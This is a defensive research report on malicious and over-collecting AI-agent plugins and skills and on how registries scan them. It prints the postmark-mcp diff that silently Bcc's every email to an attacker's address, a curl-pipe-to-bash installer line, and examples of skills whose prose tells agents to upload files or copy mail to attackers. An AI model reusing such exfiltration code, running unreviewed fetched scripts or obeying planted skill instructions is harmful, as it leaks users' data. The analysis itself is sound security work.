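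Installers add download hosts to the destinations a skill contacts. An audit on skills.sh, a directory of skills, rated one skill high risk partly because a script in it downloads and runs a program from GitHub, while the skill's metadata declares access only to `docs.dify.ai`. The scanner was right that the declaration was incomplete, and running a downloaded program deserves attention, but the program comes from the repository that Dify recommends for its command-line tool.

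*SkillsMetric* (2026) notes that static analysis can't determine whether an operation suits its context, and proposes having a language model review the skills that static analysis can't confidently classify. Its static scanner processes more than 100 skills a second, compared with about one for a model. A marketplace could likewise use static analysis to extract domains from every update, and have a model read only the updates that contain a new domain. The model could check whether the update's stated purpose explains the new domain, though a dishonest author can write a convincing explanation.

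Error reporting is harder to judge because it is supposed to send data that the user didn't ask to share. A crash report sent to an outside service helps the plugin's author find the fault. The report may need only an error message and a version number, but it can also include the invoice that caused the crash. Red Hat warns that an attacker can add a few lines that read a credential file, encode it and append it to a telemetry address, and the change will look like ordinary logging. SkillFortify flags skills that combine external network access with base64, a common way to encode data as text. That rule could catch the theft Red Hat describes, but it would also flag a harmless plugin that encodes an attachment before uploading it. To tell them apart, a reviewer has to find out what the plugin encodes and whether the receiving service needs it.

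## Postmark, Vercel and Drift: data sent through access already granted

In three incidents in 2025 and 2026, data went somewhere users hadn't intended, through access they had already granted. An email server copied outgoing messages to an outside address, a coding plugin sent its maker the text of users' shell commands, and thieves used a chat tool's access tokens to read companies' customer records.

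### postmark-mcp: a hidden copy of every email

Postmark delivers emails such as receipts and password resets for other companies' software. It keeps an official MCP server on GitHub. In September 2025 a developer with the username phanpak published a copy of that server on npm, the package registry, under the name `postmark-mcp`. Postmark says it had nothing to do with the package and hadn't published its own server on npm before the incident.

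The first versions worked as advertised. Version 1.0.16 added one line, which Idan Dardikman of the security company Koi found after Koi's software flagged the release. The line put an extra address in the blind copy (Bcc) field of every email. Simplified, the change looked like this:

```
  From: sender,
  To: recipient,
+ Bcc: "phan@giftshop.club",
```

The other recipients of an email can't see who is in the Bcc field, and the agent received only the usual success message.

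The MCP server uses the customer's key to pass each email to Postmark, which delivers it to every address in the message. The MCP server therefore never contacts `giftshop.club` itself.

Most comparisons of versions 1.0.15 and 1.0.16 would have found no difference. The customer's key already allowed the server to send mail. According to Koi, only the Bcc line changed, so the tool definition would have matched its fingerprint and passed Ameur and colleagues' re-approval rule. A network monitor would have recorded connections only to Postmark in both versions.

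Searching the code for domains might have worked, depending on what the scanner extracts. `giftshop.club` is in the new file but not the old one, so a scanner that collects anything resembling a domain would report it. A scanner that collects only web addresses, or only the hosts a program contacts, would miss it. Any of these scanners would miss an address that the program assembled as it ran.

Comparing the code is the most reliable check here, since a reviewer would have had only one new line to read. But the reviewer has to compare the package itself, because a directory that scans only an AI plugin's commits would miss version 1.0.16 if the plugin installed `postmark-mcp` from npm without pinning the version.

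A rule about recipients could have caught the copying without anyone reading the code. The agent's tool call lists the email's intended recipients. A check between the MCP server and Postmark could compare that list with the recipients on the outgoing message and block the message if an address has been added. For a company that writes to new customers every day, this works better than an allowlist of recipients. It would stop some legitimate mail, because companies use blind copies to archive correspondence, but an administrator could approve the archive's address once.

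Accounts of the package's history conflict. Koi describes a tool that developers came to trust over fifteen versions, and warns that such a tool can be legitimate for months before becoming malicious. The Hacker News (2025) reports that phanpak uploaded the package on September 15 and released version 1.0.16 on September 17. If those dates are right, the package was harmless for two days, and the case is closer to impersonation from the start than to a trusted developer turning malicious. Postmark also describes it as impersonation.

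Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails* dates Koi's report to September 25, eight days after the malicious release. A company that waited two weeks before installing any new version would have avoided this one, but it would also have received security fixes two weeks late.

The number of victims is uncertain. Koi reports 1,500 downloads a week, while The Hacker News reports 1,643 in total. Both can be right if nearly all the downloads came in one week. Koi estimates that 300 organizations were affected and that 3,000 to 15,000 emails were copied each day. It assumes that 20% of the weekly downloads were in active use, each by a separate organization that sent 10 to 50 emails a day. Koi calls the estimate a guess. Downloads are a poor measure of organizations because one developer can download a package several times.

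Koi contacted the developer, phanpak, who didn't reply but deleted the package from npm. That stopped new installations but left existing ones running, so the copying could continue until users removed the package. Koi and Postmark told users to check their email logs, where the extra recipient would appear.

### Vercel's plugin: shell commands sent as usage data

Vercel hosts websites and makes Next.js, a framework for building them. Its plugin for Claude Code and Cursor gives the agent advice on Vercel's products. In its launch notice, Vercel said the plugin observes file edits and terminal commands so it can add relevant advice to the agent's context. The notice didn't mention sending those commands to Vercel.

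In 2026 the developer Akshay Chugh found that the Vercel plugin sent the full text of every shell command to `telemetry.vercel.com` by default, even from projects that had nothing to do with Vercel. TechRadar's report on his findings, *'That felt wrong'*, noted that Vercel put the instructions for turning this off in the plugin's own directory and didn't show them during installation.

Commands can contain sensitive details. This invented one reveals a client's name, the purpose of a database and its password:

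```
psql postgres://admin:PASSWORD@payroll.client.example/salaries
```

An engineer who worked on the plugin, replying as andrewqu on the discussion site Hacker News, confirmed that Vercel collected shell commands. In Vercel's defence, he wrote that the data was anonymous because the company attached only a random identifier, that users could turn off all collection with one setting, and that Vercel collected the text of prompts only from users who agreed to it. He said the plugin ran in every project because Vercel also wanted to help people starting new ones, and that the company needed usage data to see which advice appeared too often or didn't help.

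Chugh replied that he wanted Vercel to ask before collecting anything, describe the data in plain language and limit collection to Vercel projects. He said nobody was asking it to stop collecting data entirely. Other users were more worried about secrets. One planned to tell his team to assume that every secret on a machine that had run the plugin was compromised. Another thought that anyone who lets an agent handle secrets already has a security problem. A third answered that he can confirm each of the agent's actions, whereas the plugin sent everything by default.

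This dispute involves three separate questions, and a scanner that reports only "sends data to an outside server" doesn't answer any of them.

The evidence suggests that Vercel was not acting maliciously. The data went to an address under the company's own name, the code was open to inspection, and an employee publicly explained the collection. postmark-mcp, by contrast, sent mail to its developer's private address under another company's name.

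Vercel didn't tell users enough. Its launch notice disclosed that the plugin looked at commands, but not that they left the machine. The question about prompts could also mislead users. ww-w.ai pointed out in *Delete the Vercel Claude Code Plugin. Here's Why I Did* that answering "No thanks" stopped only the collection of prompt text, while the rest of the telemetry continued. andrewqu blamed the limits of Claude Code's plugin system for the way the plugin asked for consent. Those limits may explain an awkward question, but Vercel could still have left collection off until users turned it on.

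Many users wouldn't have wanted the collection even if Vercel had explained it fully, and a company may forbid it whatever the explanation. Anonymity is a weak defense, because a command can identify a person or a client whatever identifier Vercel attaches. The plugin's main feature doesn't seem to require the transfer either. By Vercel's description, the plugin matches commands against prepared patterns inside its hooks, which run on the user's machine. Collecting shell commands from unrelated projects is therefore hard to justify under Anthropic's rule that plugins collect only the data they need.

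A comparison of domains would have been little help. Vercel owns `telemetry.vercel.com`, so an ownership check would pass, and a company that hosts its website with Vercel might already allow every address under `vercel.com`. The same address also received very different data from different versions:

| Version of the plugin | What it sent to `telemetry.vercel.com` by default |
|---|---|
| The version Chugh examined | Usage data that included full shell commands |
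| 0.32.7 | A permanent device identifier, details of each session, the names of the tools the agent called, and the skills that matched |
| 0.40.0 and later, as documented by June 2026 | A signal on first use and at most one a day after that, with random identifiers and the plugin's version number |

The entry for 0.32.7 comes from ww-w.ai's reading of the code. The last entry comes from a later README in which Vercel says it doesn't collect prompts, commands, file paths or project names. This is a large improvement, although collection is still on by default. A scanner that compared domains would have reported no difference between any two of these versions, whether collection grew or shrank.

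Comparing hooks would have been more useful. In a README saved on April 10, 2026, Vercel listed hooks that ran at the start of a session and before tool calls and file edits. The later README lists only hooks for the start of a session, though its text also mentions an observe-only step after tool calls. If an update added a hook on every tool call, a reviewer would know that the plugin could now read every command. The reviewer could then check whether the plugin sent those commands anywhere.

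A disclosure review is the check that best fits this case. A reviewer lists the fields in each outgoing request, then asks whether the plugin needs to send each one and whether the user knows about it. The full command would have failed both tests. Such reviews take time, but software can help find the requests. ww-w.ai began investigating the plugin after a scanner he was building flagged something on his own machine. He assumed it was a false alarm and opened Vercel's code as a good example to compare with his own. A well-known name can therefore make a reviewer less suspicious, even when the scanner has worked correctly.

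### Salesloft Drift: the same scopes in a thief's hands

Salesloft's Drift is an AI chat agent that businesses put on their websites, not an add-on for Claude or ChatGPT. Businesses connected it to Salesforce, where they keep their customer records, through OAuth tokens like those that remote MCP servers use. SpecterOps' *The Salesloft–Drift Breach* (2025) points out that Salesloft held these tokens in its own cloud, so a break-in there also exposed its customers' Salesforce data.

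Attackers had access to Salesloft's GitHub account between March and June 2025, then entered Drift's cloud environment and took the tokens, according to the company's account in Infosecurity Magazine's *Salesloft*. Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025) traced the thefts for Google in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift*. From August 8 to at least August 18, the attackers exported large amounts of data from Salesforce and searched it for passwords and access keys. Google told The Hacker News (2025) that the campaign may have affected more than 700 organizations.

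Comparing versions of Drift would not have revealed the theft, because it didn't require a new version. The tokens kept the same scopes, and the requests still went to Salesforce, but the sender, the requests' origin and the amount of data retrieved changed.

Cloudflare (2025), one of the victims, published a timeline that shows when other checks could have helped. The attacker first logged in to Cloudflare's Salesforce account on the evening of August 12, explored the records for several days, and exported the text of its support cases on August 17 in just over three minutes. An alert on large exports would probably have come too late, unless it also cut off access automatically. An alert on the unfamiliar address used on August 12 would have given Cloudflare more than four days to act before the export. That address belonged to Amazon's cloud, where Drift also ran, so a rule that accepted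 any Amazon address would have missed it. Cloudflare learned of the theft on August 23, three days after Salesloft had revoked the tokens.

*The Salesloft incident* (2025), by the identity company Okta, reports that someone tried a stolen Drift token on Okta's Salesforce account and failed because the account accepted connections only from approved addresses. Other customers could have set the same restriction, since Salesloft had published Drift's address ranges before the attack, according to Okta's *First Drift, now Gainsight* (2025). Okta also recommends tying each token to the client that requested it, so that a copy doesn't work on another machine. The incident didn't test this measure, and Okta sells products that support it, so the evidence for it is much weaker than the evidence for restricting addresses.

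### What a domain or scope leaves out

Domains and scopes don't show which account or recipient a transfer involves, what it contains, why it was made, or who is using the token.

An update can send data to a different account on the same service. Suppose the invoice plugin stores documents with a large cloud provider under the user's key. If an update replaces that key with the plugin author's, the invoices still go to the same domain with the same kind of permission, but they are stored in the author's account. An allowlist can't distinguish the two accounts because the provider serves both from one address.

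Each of these details needs a different check:

| What changes | Example | Check that could notice | Main limit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Account | The invoice plugin's replaced key | Comparing the credentials that the code uses | Requires the code |
| Recipient | postmark-mcp | Comparing the code, or a rule on recipients | The rule has to read each message before delivery |
| Content | Vercel's shell commands | Inspecting outgoing data | Encoding or encryption can hide the data |
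| Purpose | Vercel's use of commands to improve its product | Disclosure review | A reviewer can't verify what happens after the data arrives |
| Person using the token | Drift | Restricting addresses or tying tokens to a client | An attacker working inside the provider's own systems may pass |

Alerts on data volume would have been useful mainly for Drift. In the Postmark case, the hidden Bcc line added a recipient to messages the server was already sending, so the number of requests stayed the same. Vercel's plugin sent short pieces of text throughout a session, as ordinary usage reporting does. An alert sensitive enough to detect either case would also go off for a lot of harmless traffic.

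## ClawHub: scanners that judge whether a skill is malicious

ClawHub is the public registry of skills for OpenClaw, an agent that people run on their own computers. Its scanners estimate whether a skill is malicious, which is a different test from comparing a new version with the approved one. An update can widen a skill's access for legitimate reasons, and the hidden Bcc line in `postmark-mcp` stole data without widening the package's access. A registry also receives first versions from strangers, which have no approved version to compare with.

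### The malicious uploads of early 2026

Attackers tried to publish malware on ClawHub as soon as it opened. Koi (2026) checked 2,857 skills and found that 341, about 12%, were malicious. According to The Hacker News (2026), 335 of these used a fake prerequisite to install Atomic Stealer, a program that steals passwords, browser data and cryptocurrency wallets from Macs. By February 16, the registry had grown to more than 10,700 skills, and Koi had counted 824 malicious ones. Some of the new malicious skills were disguised as security scanners.

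VirusTotal, a Google service that checks files with dozens of antivirus engines, found many of the same kind. Its *From Automation to Infection* (2026) traces 314 malicious skills to a single ClawHub account. One of them, called "Yahoo Finance", contained almost no code, so no antivirus engine flagged it. The setup instructions for Windows were to download a password-protected archive from GitHub and run the program inside. Mac users got a link to an encoded script, which fetched the malware Atomic Stealer from another server. Several engines recognized both programs as malicious, but neither was in the skill itself.

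An attacker could use the same trick in an update by adding a "required" helper to the setup instructions of a skill that people already trust. An allowlist that already included GitHub wouldn't catch the Windows download.

### How ClawHub screens a skill

In February 2026 OpenClaw began checking every published skill with VirusTotal. According to OpenClaw, ClawHub computed a fingerprint of the skill's files and looked it up in VirusTotal's records. If VirusTotal had no analysis, ClawHub uploaded the files, and a Google language model read the instructions and scripts and summarized what they did. ClawHub automatically approved skills classified as benign, put a warning on suspicious ones and blocked downloads of malicious ones.

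ClawHub also rescanned every active skill daily. A rescan can catch a malicious skill even if its files haven't changed, because antivirus companies may have learned to recognize it since the last scan. OpenClaw called the scan "not a silver bullet" and warned that it could miss harmful instructions written in ordinary language.

By June OpenClaw had added other scanners, and each new version now goes through three of them before it appears in the registry:

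| Scanner | What it examines | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | The skill's files, using about 70 antivirus engines and records of known bad addresses | New malware, and access that is too broad for the task |
| Static analysis | Patterns in the code and text, such as dangerous commands or exposed passwords | Whether the skill's purpose explains the pattern |
| SkillSpector, made by NVIDIA | The instructions and declared capabilities, using fixed rules and a language model | Malware in bundled code, and what happens when the skill runs |

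A language model then classifies the skill as clean, suspicious or malicious, based on the three results, where the skill came from and its moderation history. OpenClaw calls this step ClawScan. A SkillSpector finding doesn't block a skill by itself.

ClawHub publishes a Skill Card with each skill, listing who published it, what it can do and what ClawScan found. OpenClaw's description of the pipeline doesn't mention comparing a new version with the previous one. But ClawHub compiles the card itself instead of relying on the publisher, so a company could save the card for version 1 and compare it with the card for version 2.

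Between February and May 2026, Unit 42, a security research group at Palo Alto Networks, found five malicious skills on ClawHub that screening had not blocked.

### How rarely the scanners agree

*ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) measured how often the three scanners flag the same skills. All six authors work for OpenClaw or NVIDIA. They used the version of each of 67,453 public skills that was current on May 31, 2026, and counted a skill as flagged if a scanner rated it suspicious or malicious. At least one scanner flagged 35,600 skills, more than half of the total.

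For each pair of scanners, the overlap is

number of skills that both flagged ÷ number that at least one flagged

| Pair | Skills both flagged | Overlap | Highest possible overlap |
|---|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal and static analysis | 586 | 6.5% | 85% |
| VirusTotal and SkillSpector | 3,286 | 9.4% | 16% |
| Static analysis and SkillSpector | 3,511 | 10.4% | 13% |

Only one scanner flagged 81.9% of the skills that had any flag. All three flagged just 468 skills, which is 0.69% of the registry.

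The last column of the table shows the highest overlap each pair could have, given how many skills each scanner flagged. It is low for both pairs that include SkillSpector because SkillSpector flagged 32,856 skills, nearly half the registry, while VirusTotal flagged 5,225 and static analysis 4,434. SkillSpector accounts for 91% of the skills that only one scanner flagged. It also flagged 79% of the skills that static analysis did, so their 10.4% overlap makes them seem to disagree more than they do.

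The low overlap between VirusTotal and static analysis is harder to explain this way. The two scanners flagged similar numbers of skills but had only 586 in common, and chance alone would have produced about 340. After correcting for chance, Koc and colleagues found only slight agreement between every pair of scanners.

### Why two scanners can disagree and both be right

ClawHub's scanners test for different things, so they can disagree without either being wrong. One skill in the study copies a user's meeting notes to local files, using the user's existing login. SkillSpector gave it a risk score of 100, and ClawScan rated it clean. Both results are reasonable, because the skill handles private notes and a login token, but does so openly and for its advertised purpose.

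A well-meaning author's skill can also get a worse verdict. A known OpenClaw maintainer published a skill for controlling Roku televisions, and ClawScan rated it suspicious because it also accepted commands through the messaging service Telegram without clearly disclosing this. A reviewer of updates would want to know about that kind of access, whatever the author's intentions.

A "malicious" verdict doesn't necessarily mean that a skill works against its user. ClawScan gave that verdict to a browser automation skill that openly promoted ways around CAPTCHAs and bot detection. The skill might do exactly what its user wants, but ClawHub can reasonably refuse to distribute it.

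The scanners' results vary a lot with ClawScan's verdict:

| ClawScan's verdict | Skills | VirusTotal flagged | Static analysis flagged | SkillSpector flagged | No scanner flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean | 41,743 | 4.4% | 3.2% | 32.7% | 63.4% |
| Suspicious | 25,504 | 12.7% | 12.0% | 75.3% | 20.9% |
| Malicious | 206 | 72.8% | 12.6% | 6.8% | 24.3% |

SkillSpector flagged a smaller share of the malicious skills than of the clean ones. Koc and colleagues attribute this to SkillSpector's focus on instructions and declared capabilities, since malware is often in bundled code. They also counted a missing result as no flag, so part of the gap could come from skills that SkillSpector never finished scanning.

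The 72.8% for VirusTotal isn't its recall, because the released labels are ClawScan's automated verdicts, which no human checked. ClawScan had also read VirusTotal's results before it gave those verdicts. The study therefore measures agreement between scanners and provides little evidence about which of them is right.

SkillSpector's most common finding was that a skill had more access than it needed, which the study counted in 11% of clean skills and 20% of suspicious ones. Findings about data leaving the machine distinguished the two groups even less, at 2.9% and 3.9%, because many legitimate skills are meant to send data somewhere, such as one that delivers email summaries to a chat channel. Findings of dangerous code execution distinguished them much better, at 0.7% and 5.2%. If ClawScan's verdicts are reliable, an update that starts sending data out deserves less suspicion for that alone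 than one that starts running risky code.

ClawScan rated 38% of all skills suspicious. If ClawHub still puts a warning on each suspicious skill, as it did in February, the warning is too common to be very informative.

### Harmless skills that a company may still forbid

A company may still forbid what a skill does even if scanners rate the skill clean. In *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action*, Rohit Taneja and Travis Weber examined 66,192 skill versions from the dataset that OpenClaw released with its study. All three scanners and ClawScan had rated 29,257 of them clean. Among these, they found 705 whose instructions include an action that many operators forbid an agent to take unsupervised. In 658, the action is to download code from the internet and run it. Most of the others read credentials or delete files.

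Their main example is an ordinary installer from a real software company. With the company's address replaced, the command looks like this:

```
curl -fsSL https://cli.vendor.example/install.sh | bash
```

A skill may download a script and run it immediately. Many companies distribute software this way, and a malware scanner is right to pass it. A two-person startup might let an agent run the script, but a bank might forbid its agents to run any script that nobody at the bank has reviewed. ClawHub can judge whether the skill is malicious, but it can't decide for both whether the action is permitted, because that depends on the rules and machines of whoever installs the skill.

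As with an unpinned package, the company can change the script without changing the skill's fingerprint, so a reviewer of updates would have to pin the script too.

One publisher, oomol, accounts for 506 of the 705 skills because it repeats the same installer line across its catalog. The remaining 199 come from 134 publishers, nearly all with one skill each, so the practice is fairly widespread even without oomol.

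Taneja and Weber checked 100 of the 705 by hand and judged 92 to be correct detections (95% confidence interval 84.8% to 96.5%). Most of the errors were commands that downloaded data and only formatted it for display. They found no sign of malicious intent in the 92. This is limited evidence that the skills are harmless, because one person did the checking and read only the documented commands, which a careful attacker would make look ordinary. The detector also ignores instructions written as prose, so it may have missed other skills. It counts instructions in skills rather than agents' actual behavior, which Taneja and Weber tested separately.

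Taneja and Weber also didn't survey operators. The claim that many operators forbid these actions rests on two published security standards, one from the Center for Internet Security and one from the US standards agency NIST. Taneja and Weber work for Pheo, which sells software that checks each of an agent's commands before it runs, so the finding helps make the case for their product. But the distinction doesn't depend on the product, since any company that bans unreviewed scripts would need some check besides ClawHub's verdict.

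Taneja and Weber also found that instructions to download and run code were slightly more common among the skills that every scanner passed (2.25%) than in the whole dataset (1.73%), so by this measure they are no sign of malice. They built a detector for data sent to a fixed domain but dropped it because it flagged 4.4% of the clean skills. Ordinary connections to outside services also send data to a fixed domain. The 4.4% figure is approximate because they measured it before fixing an error in their code, but it suggests that a registry that stopped every skill that sends data to a fixed domain would stop many harmless ones.

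### Recall and false alarms in MalSkillBench

OpenClaw's data can't show how many malicious skills a scanner misses, because nobody has established which skills in it are malicious. *MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, 2026) provides a test set for measuring this, with 3,944 malicious skills and 4,000 harmless ones.

Only 703 of the malicious skills had appeared on public registries. Another 27 came from the test suites of existing scanners. Guo and colleagues generated the other 3,214 in three steps:

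1. They gave a language model an ordinary skill and examples of a known attack. The model was a version with its tendency to refuse harmful requests removed.
2. The model combined them into a malicious skill that still looked useful.
3. An agent ran the skill in a sandbox. The skill entered the test set only if system records or a second language model confirmed the intended attack.

For the harmless skills, they took the most downloaded ones on ClawHub. They tested nine scanners, some in more than one mode. These are five of the results:

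| Scanner | Recall | False alarms among 4,000 harmless skills |
|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 21.6% | 4 (0.1%) |
| Snyk Agent Scan | 28.7% | 82 (2.1%) |
| AI-Infra-Guard, from Tencent | 86.6% | 620 (15.5%) |
| Cisco Skill Scanner with a language model | 92.7% | 1,465 (36.6%) |
| Sentry Skill Scanner with a language model | 98.4% | 937 (23.4%) |

The last three scanners use language models. They find far more of the malicious skills because they read the instructions together with the code and infer what the skill is for. But they raise many more false alarms, because harmless skills also install helpers, run shell commands and request access tokens. The scanner has to decide whether the skill's purpose justifies these actions, and language models often get this wrong.

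The ranking changes on the 703 real malicious skills. VirusTotal's recall rises to 87.9% and Snyk's to 77.2%, while AI-Infra-Guard's falls to 74.0%. The real skills are very similar. Two accounts published 569 of them, and 609 deliver malware. VirusTotal caught 99.3% of those 609, but only 3 of the 18 skills that sent users' data elsewhere and 3 of the 33 that stole credentials. Each of the three language-model scanners caught 14 or 15 of the 18 that sent data elsewhere. The sample is small, but these results are more relevant than VirusTotal's overall recall to a company worried about an update that quietly sends out data.

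VirusTotal's recall on the real skills may also be higher than it would have been on the day each skill appeared. Guo and colleagues found these skills through public reports, so antivirus companies had already had time to add them to their records. In February, no engine had flagged the "Yahoo Finance" skill. A malicious update is new, so its fingerprint won't be in anyone's records.

The count of four false alarms is also doubtful. The harmless skills had already passed ClawHub's screening, which included VirusTotal, so skills that VirusTotal tends to flag wrongly may never have reached the test set. In OpenClaw's data, VirusTotal flagged 4.4% of the skills that ClawScan rated clean. Some of those may be malicious skills that ClawScan missed, but the actual false-positive rate could easily be well above 0.1%.

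Attacks written as instructions were harder to detect than attacks in code. AI-Infra-Guard caught 99.2% of the attacks in code but 74.8% of those in instructions, and Cisco's scanner caught 96.5% and 83.1%, respectively. The paper's abstract describes the strongest scanner as collapsing on instruction attacks, but in the detailed results Sentry's scanner caught 97.6% of them.

Simple ways of combining scanners didn't help much. Guo and colleagues added a scanner for malicious software packages and a detector for prompt injection (text that hijacks a model's behavior) to the Sentry scanner and to AI-Infra-Guard. When they required all three tools to agree, fewer than 2% of harmless skills triggered an alarm, but recall dropped to about 36%. When a flag from any one tool was enough, the balance of recall and false alarms was no better than before. ClawHub's method, in which a language model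 weighs the evidence, might do better than either rule, but ClawScan has no published recall figure to test this against.

### Malicious skills on two other registries

Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Do Not Mention This to the User*, looked for malicious skills on skills.rest and skillsmp, two registries that collect skills from public GitHub repositories. They started with 98,380 skills in January 2026 and searched them for suspicious patterns, partly with a language model, which left 4,287 candidates. They ran each candidate in an isolated container with fake passwords and keys it could steal, and 762 did something suspicious. Two researchers reviewed those 762 and confirmed 157 as malicious, or 0.16% of the original set. The registries removed all 157 after Liu and colleagues reported them.

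As on ClawHub, a few publishers caused much of the harm. One actor published 85 of the 157 skills, each imitating a different brand.

Liu and colleagues recorded 632 security problems in these 157 skills, and only 4 were excessive permissions, partly because the format gives authors few permissions to request. But 115 of the skills did something their descriptions didn't reveal, and undocumented network endpoints made up 47% of those hidden features. Comparing a skill's description with the addresses it contacts is therefore a better way to find such skills than looking for excessive permissions.

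One malicious skill was a near-exact copy of a legitimate skill for making PowerPoint files, with three added lines that told the agent to run a "backup" script that uploaded the user's files to an outside server. A reviewer comparing the two would have seen the addition at once. But a version check compares a skill only with earlier versions of the same listing, and this listing had none. A registry could catch such copies by comparing each new skill with popular ones it closely resembles.

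Another skill instructed the agent to blind-copy an attacker on emails without asking the user or mentioning it. `postmark-mcp` did the same thing in code, but this skill's instruction was written in prose, so there was no code for a code scanner to detect.

The real number of malicious skills is probably higher than 157. Each container ran for at most 60 seconds, and when Liu and colleagues reviewed a sample of the unconfirmed candidates, 93% contained triggers that the test hadn't set off. A trigger doesn't prove that a skill is malicious, but some of those skills could attack under conditions that the test didn't create.

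### What the rates mean for 10,000 submissions

Suppose a registry receives 10,000 skills and 1% of them are malicious. That makes 100 malicious skills and 9,900 harmless ones. With the rates that Guo and colleagues measured, Snyk's scanner would flag 28.7% of the 100, or about 29. It would also flag 82 in every 4,000 of the harmless skills, or about 203. The same calculation for all five scanners gives:

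| Scanner | Malicious skills flagged | Harmless skills flagged | Share of flags that are correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 22 | 10 | 69% |
| Snyk | 29 | 203 | 12% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 87 | 1,530 | 5% |
| Sentry with a language model | 98 | 2,320 | 4% |
| Cisco with a language model | 93 | 3,630 | 2% |

A registry might reasonably block a skill automatically when VirusTotal flags it, but it would still let through 78 of the 100 malicious skills. With Sentry's scanner, it would let through only 2, but people would have to review about 2,400 flagged skills to find the other 98. OpenClaw processes thousands of new versions a day, so 10,000 submissions would arrive within days.

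The 1% is an assumption, and the share of flags that are correct depends heavily on it. Koi's first count on ClawHub implies 12%, while Liu and colleagues confirmed 0.16% on the other two registries. With Snyk's rates, about 66% of flags would be correct at 12% and about 2% at 0.16%. So the same flag could justify blocking a skill during a wave of attacks but only a quick look a few months later.

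VirusTotal's good result depends on its very low false-positive rate. If that rate were 4.4%, as OpenClaw's data might suggest, VirusTotal would flag about 440 harmless skills instead of 10, and only 5% of its flags would be correct.

None of these rates comes from a test on updates. Updates to established skills are probably malicious less often than uploads from new accounts. If 10 of 10,000 updates were malicious, Snyk's scanner would find about 3 of them and raise 205 false alarms.

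## Testing and watching plugins as they run

ClawHub's scanners rely mainly on a skill's files, which often don't show which access the task needs, so the scanners raise many false alarms. Running the plugin gives further evidence. A directory can run it in a test environment before approving it. After approval, a monitor can repeat the same requests to the plugin's tools from time to time and compare the answers with the original ones. Software on the user's machine can also check each action when the agent attempts it.

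Suppose version 2 of the invoice plugin searches the inbox for bank statements and uploads them with the invoices. A test reveals this only if the test inbox contains a bank statement, and replaying requests reveals it only if the plugin's answers change. A check on each action can catch the upload, but it needs a rule that distinguishes bank statements from invoices.

### Decoys in a test environment

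A sandbox test often finds little because nothing in the sandbox sets off the behaviour. Li, Ying and colleagues (2026), in *SkillSentry*, describe a system that uses a skill's own files to decide what the test environment should contain. It works like this:

1. A language model works out what the advertised task needs, including files, operations and destinations. A skill can't extend this list by requesting more permissions.
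2. The system searches the skill's files for behaviour that might go beyond the list. For each case it writes a test plan with a possible trigger, the expected action and the evidence that would prove the action happened. It drops any plan that the files don't support.
3. It simulates two environments. One contains only what the task needs. The other also contains a decoy, such as a fake credential or private file, and the system records any contact with it.
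4. In each environment, an agent attempts the same task with the skill and without it, which makes four runs.
5. The system ignores anything the agent also did without the skill. It reports a violation only if the remaining action was completed, the skill's files explain it and the task didn't require it.

For the invoice plugin, the decoy would be a bank statement in the test inbox. Uploading an invoice might be part of the task, but uploading the statement would not be. If a run never triggers the suspected behaviour, SkillSentry reports the test as unresolved instead of marking the skill as safe.

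One skill in the study was described as deleting temporary files only after the user confirmed. Skill Vetter, a scanner that has a language model read the whole skill, accepted that description. SkillSentry put decoy files in the folder and gave no confirmation, and the skill deleted them anyway. SkillSentry classified the skill as malicious, but the test shows only that the skill's behavior did not match its description, which could be a programming mistake.

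Li and colleagues compared SkillSentry with other scanners on SkillTrustBench, a test set from Tencent, and on MalSkillBench:

| Scanner | SkillTrustBench recall | SkillTrustBench false positives | MalSkillBench recall | MalSkillBench false positives |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SkillSentry | 96.12% | 4.15% | 94.74% | 2.33% |
| Cisco with a language model | 97.03% | 53.68% | 96.15% | 38.78% |
| SkillSpector with a language model | 91.15% | 45.22% | 53.25% | 20.88% |
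| Skill Vetter, run in OpenClaw | 97.52% | 49.48% | 98.73% | 3.88% |

On SkillTrustBench, Cisco's scanner and SkillSentry caught nearly the same share of harmful skills, but Cisco's also flagged more than half of the harmless ones. Li and colleagues attribute the difference to legitimate skills that have a lot of access, because their files contain the same operations as malicious ones. SkillSentry can check whether an action happens only when the skill is present and whether the task requires that action.

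At these rates, if 1% of 10,000 submissions were malicious, reviewers would get about 500 flagged skills from SkillSentry and 5,400 from Cisco's scanner. Even with SkillSentry, only about 19% of the flags would be correct.

SkillSentry's advantage is less clear on MalSkillBench, where Skill Vetter found more of the harmful skills with only slightly more false alarms. But when Li and colleagues used known techniques to disguise harmful skills, Skill Vetter found at most 22% of them in each of the four tests. SkillSentry found between 76% and 100%, although its false-positive rate reached 18% in one test.

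The system works much better when it both reads a skill's files and runs the skill. When it ran skills without first using their files to choose what to test, it caught 8% of the harmful skills on one test set and 4% on the other. Nearly all the detection rates in this comparison are multiples of 4%, which suggests about 25 harmful skills in each set, so the rates are imprecise. Removing the check that an action was completed raised the average false-positive rate from 3.24% to 34.09%.

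The closest test to a malicious update started with clean skills and inserted a harmful capability. SkillSentry had a false-positive rate of 3.94%, compared with 29.47% for SkillSpector with a language model. SkillSpector did slightly better on F1 (89.63% against 86.32%), a score that combines recall with the share of flags that are correct. For real updates, a directory could use the approved version as the control instead of running the agent with no skill, so that any new action would come from the update. Li and colleagues didn't test this.

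SkillSentry took about two minutes per skill on a sample from SkillTrustBench, and its language model processed roughly 188,000 input tokens (pieces of text). Cisco's scanner took 51 seconds and used about 9,000. A registry that receives thousands of versions a day might reserve SkillSentry for updates that widen access.

### Replaying the same requests

An approved plugin can change its behaviour while its version and tool definitions stay the same. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *ProbeID*, propose checking for this by repeating old requests. At approval, their system generates up to 512 requests that fit a tool's input schema and records the answers. Later it sends some or all of those requests again, removes details that normally vary, such as timestamps, and measures how different the answers are:

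D = (d₁ + d₂ + … + dₘ) ÷ m

Here m is the number of requests, and each d ranges from 0 (the same answer) to 1 (a completely different answer). If the average, D, is above a set threshold, ProbeID refuses the tool. The threshold has to allow for tools that give slightly different answers each time.

Suppose a change affects a share φ of possible inputs. The chance that m random requests include at least one affected input is

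1 − (1 − φ)ᵐ

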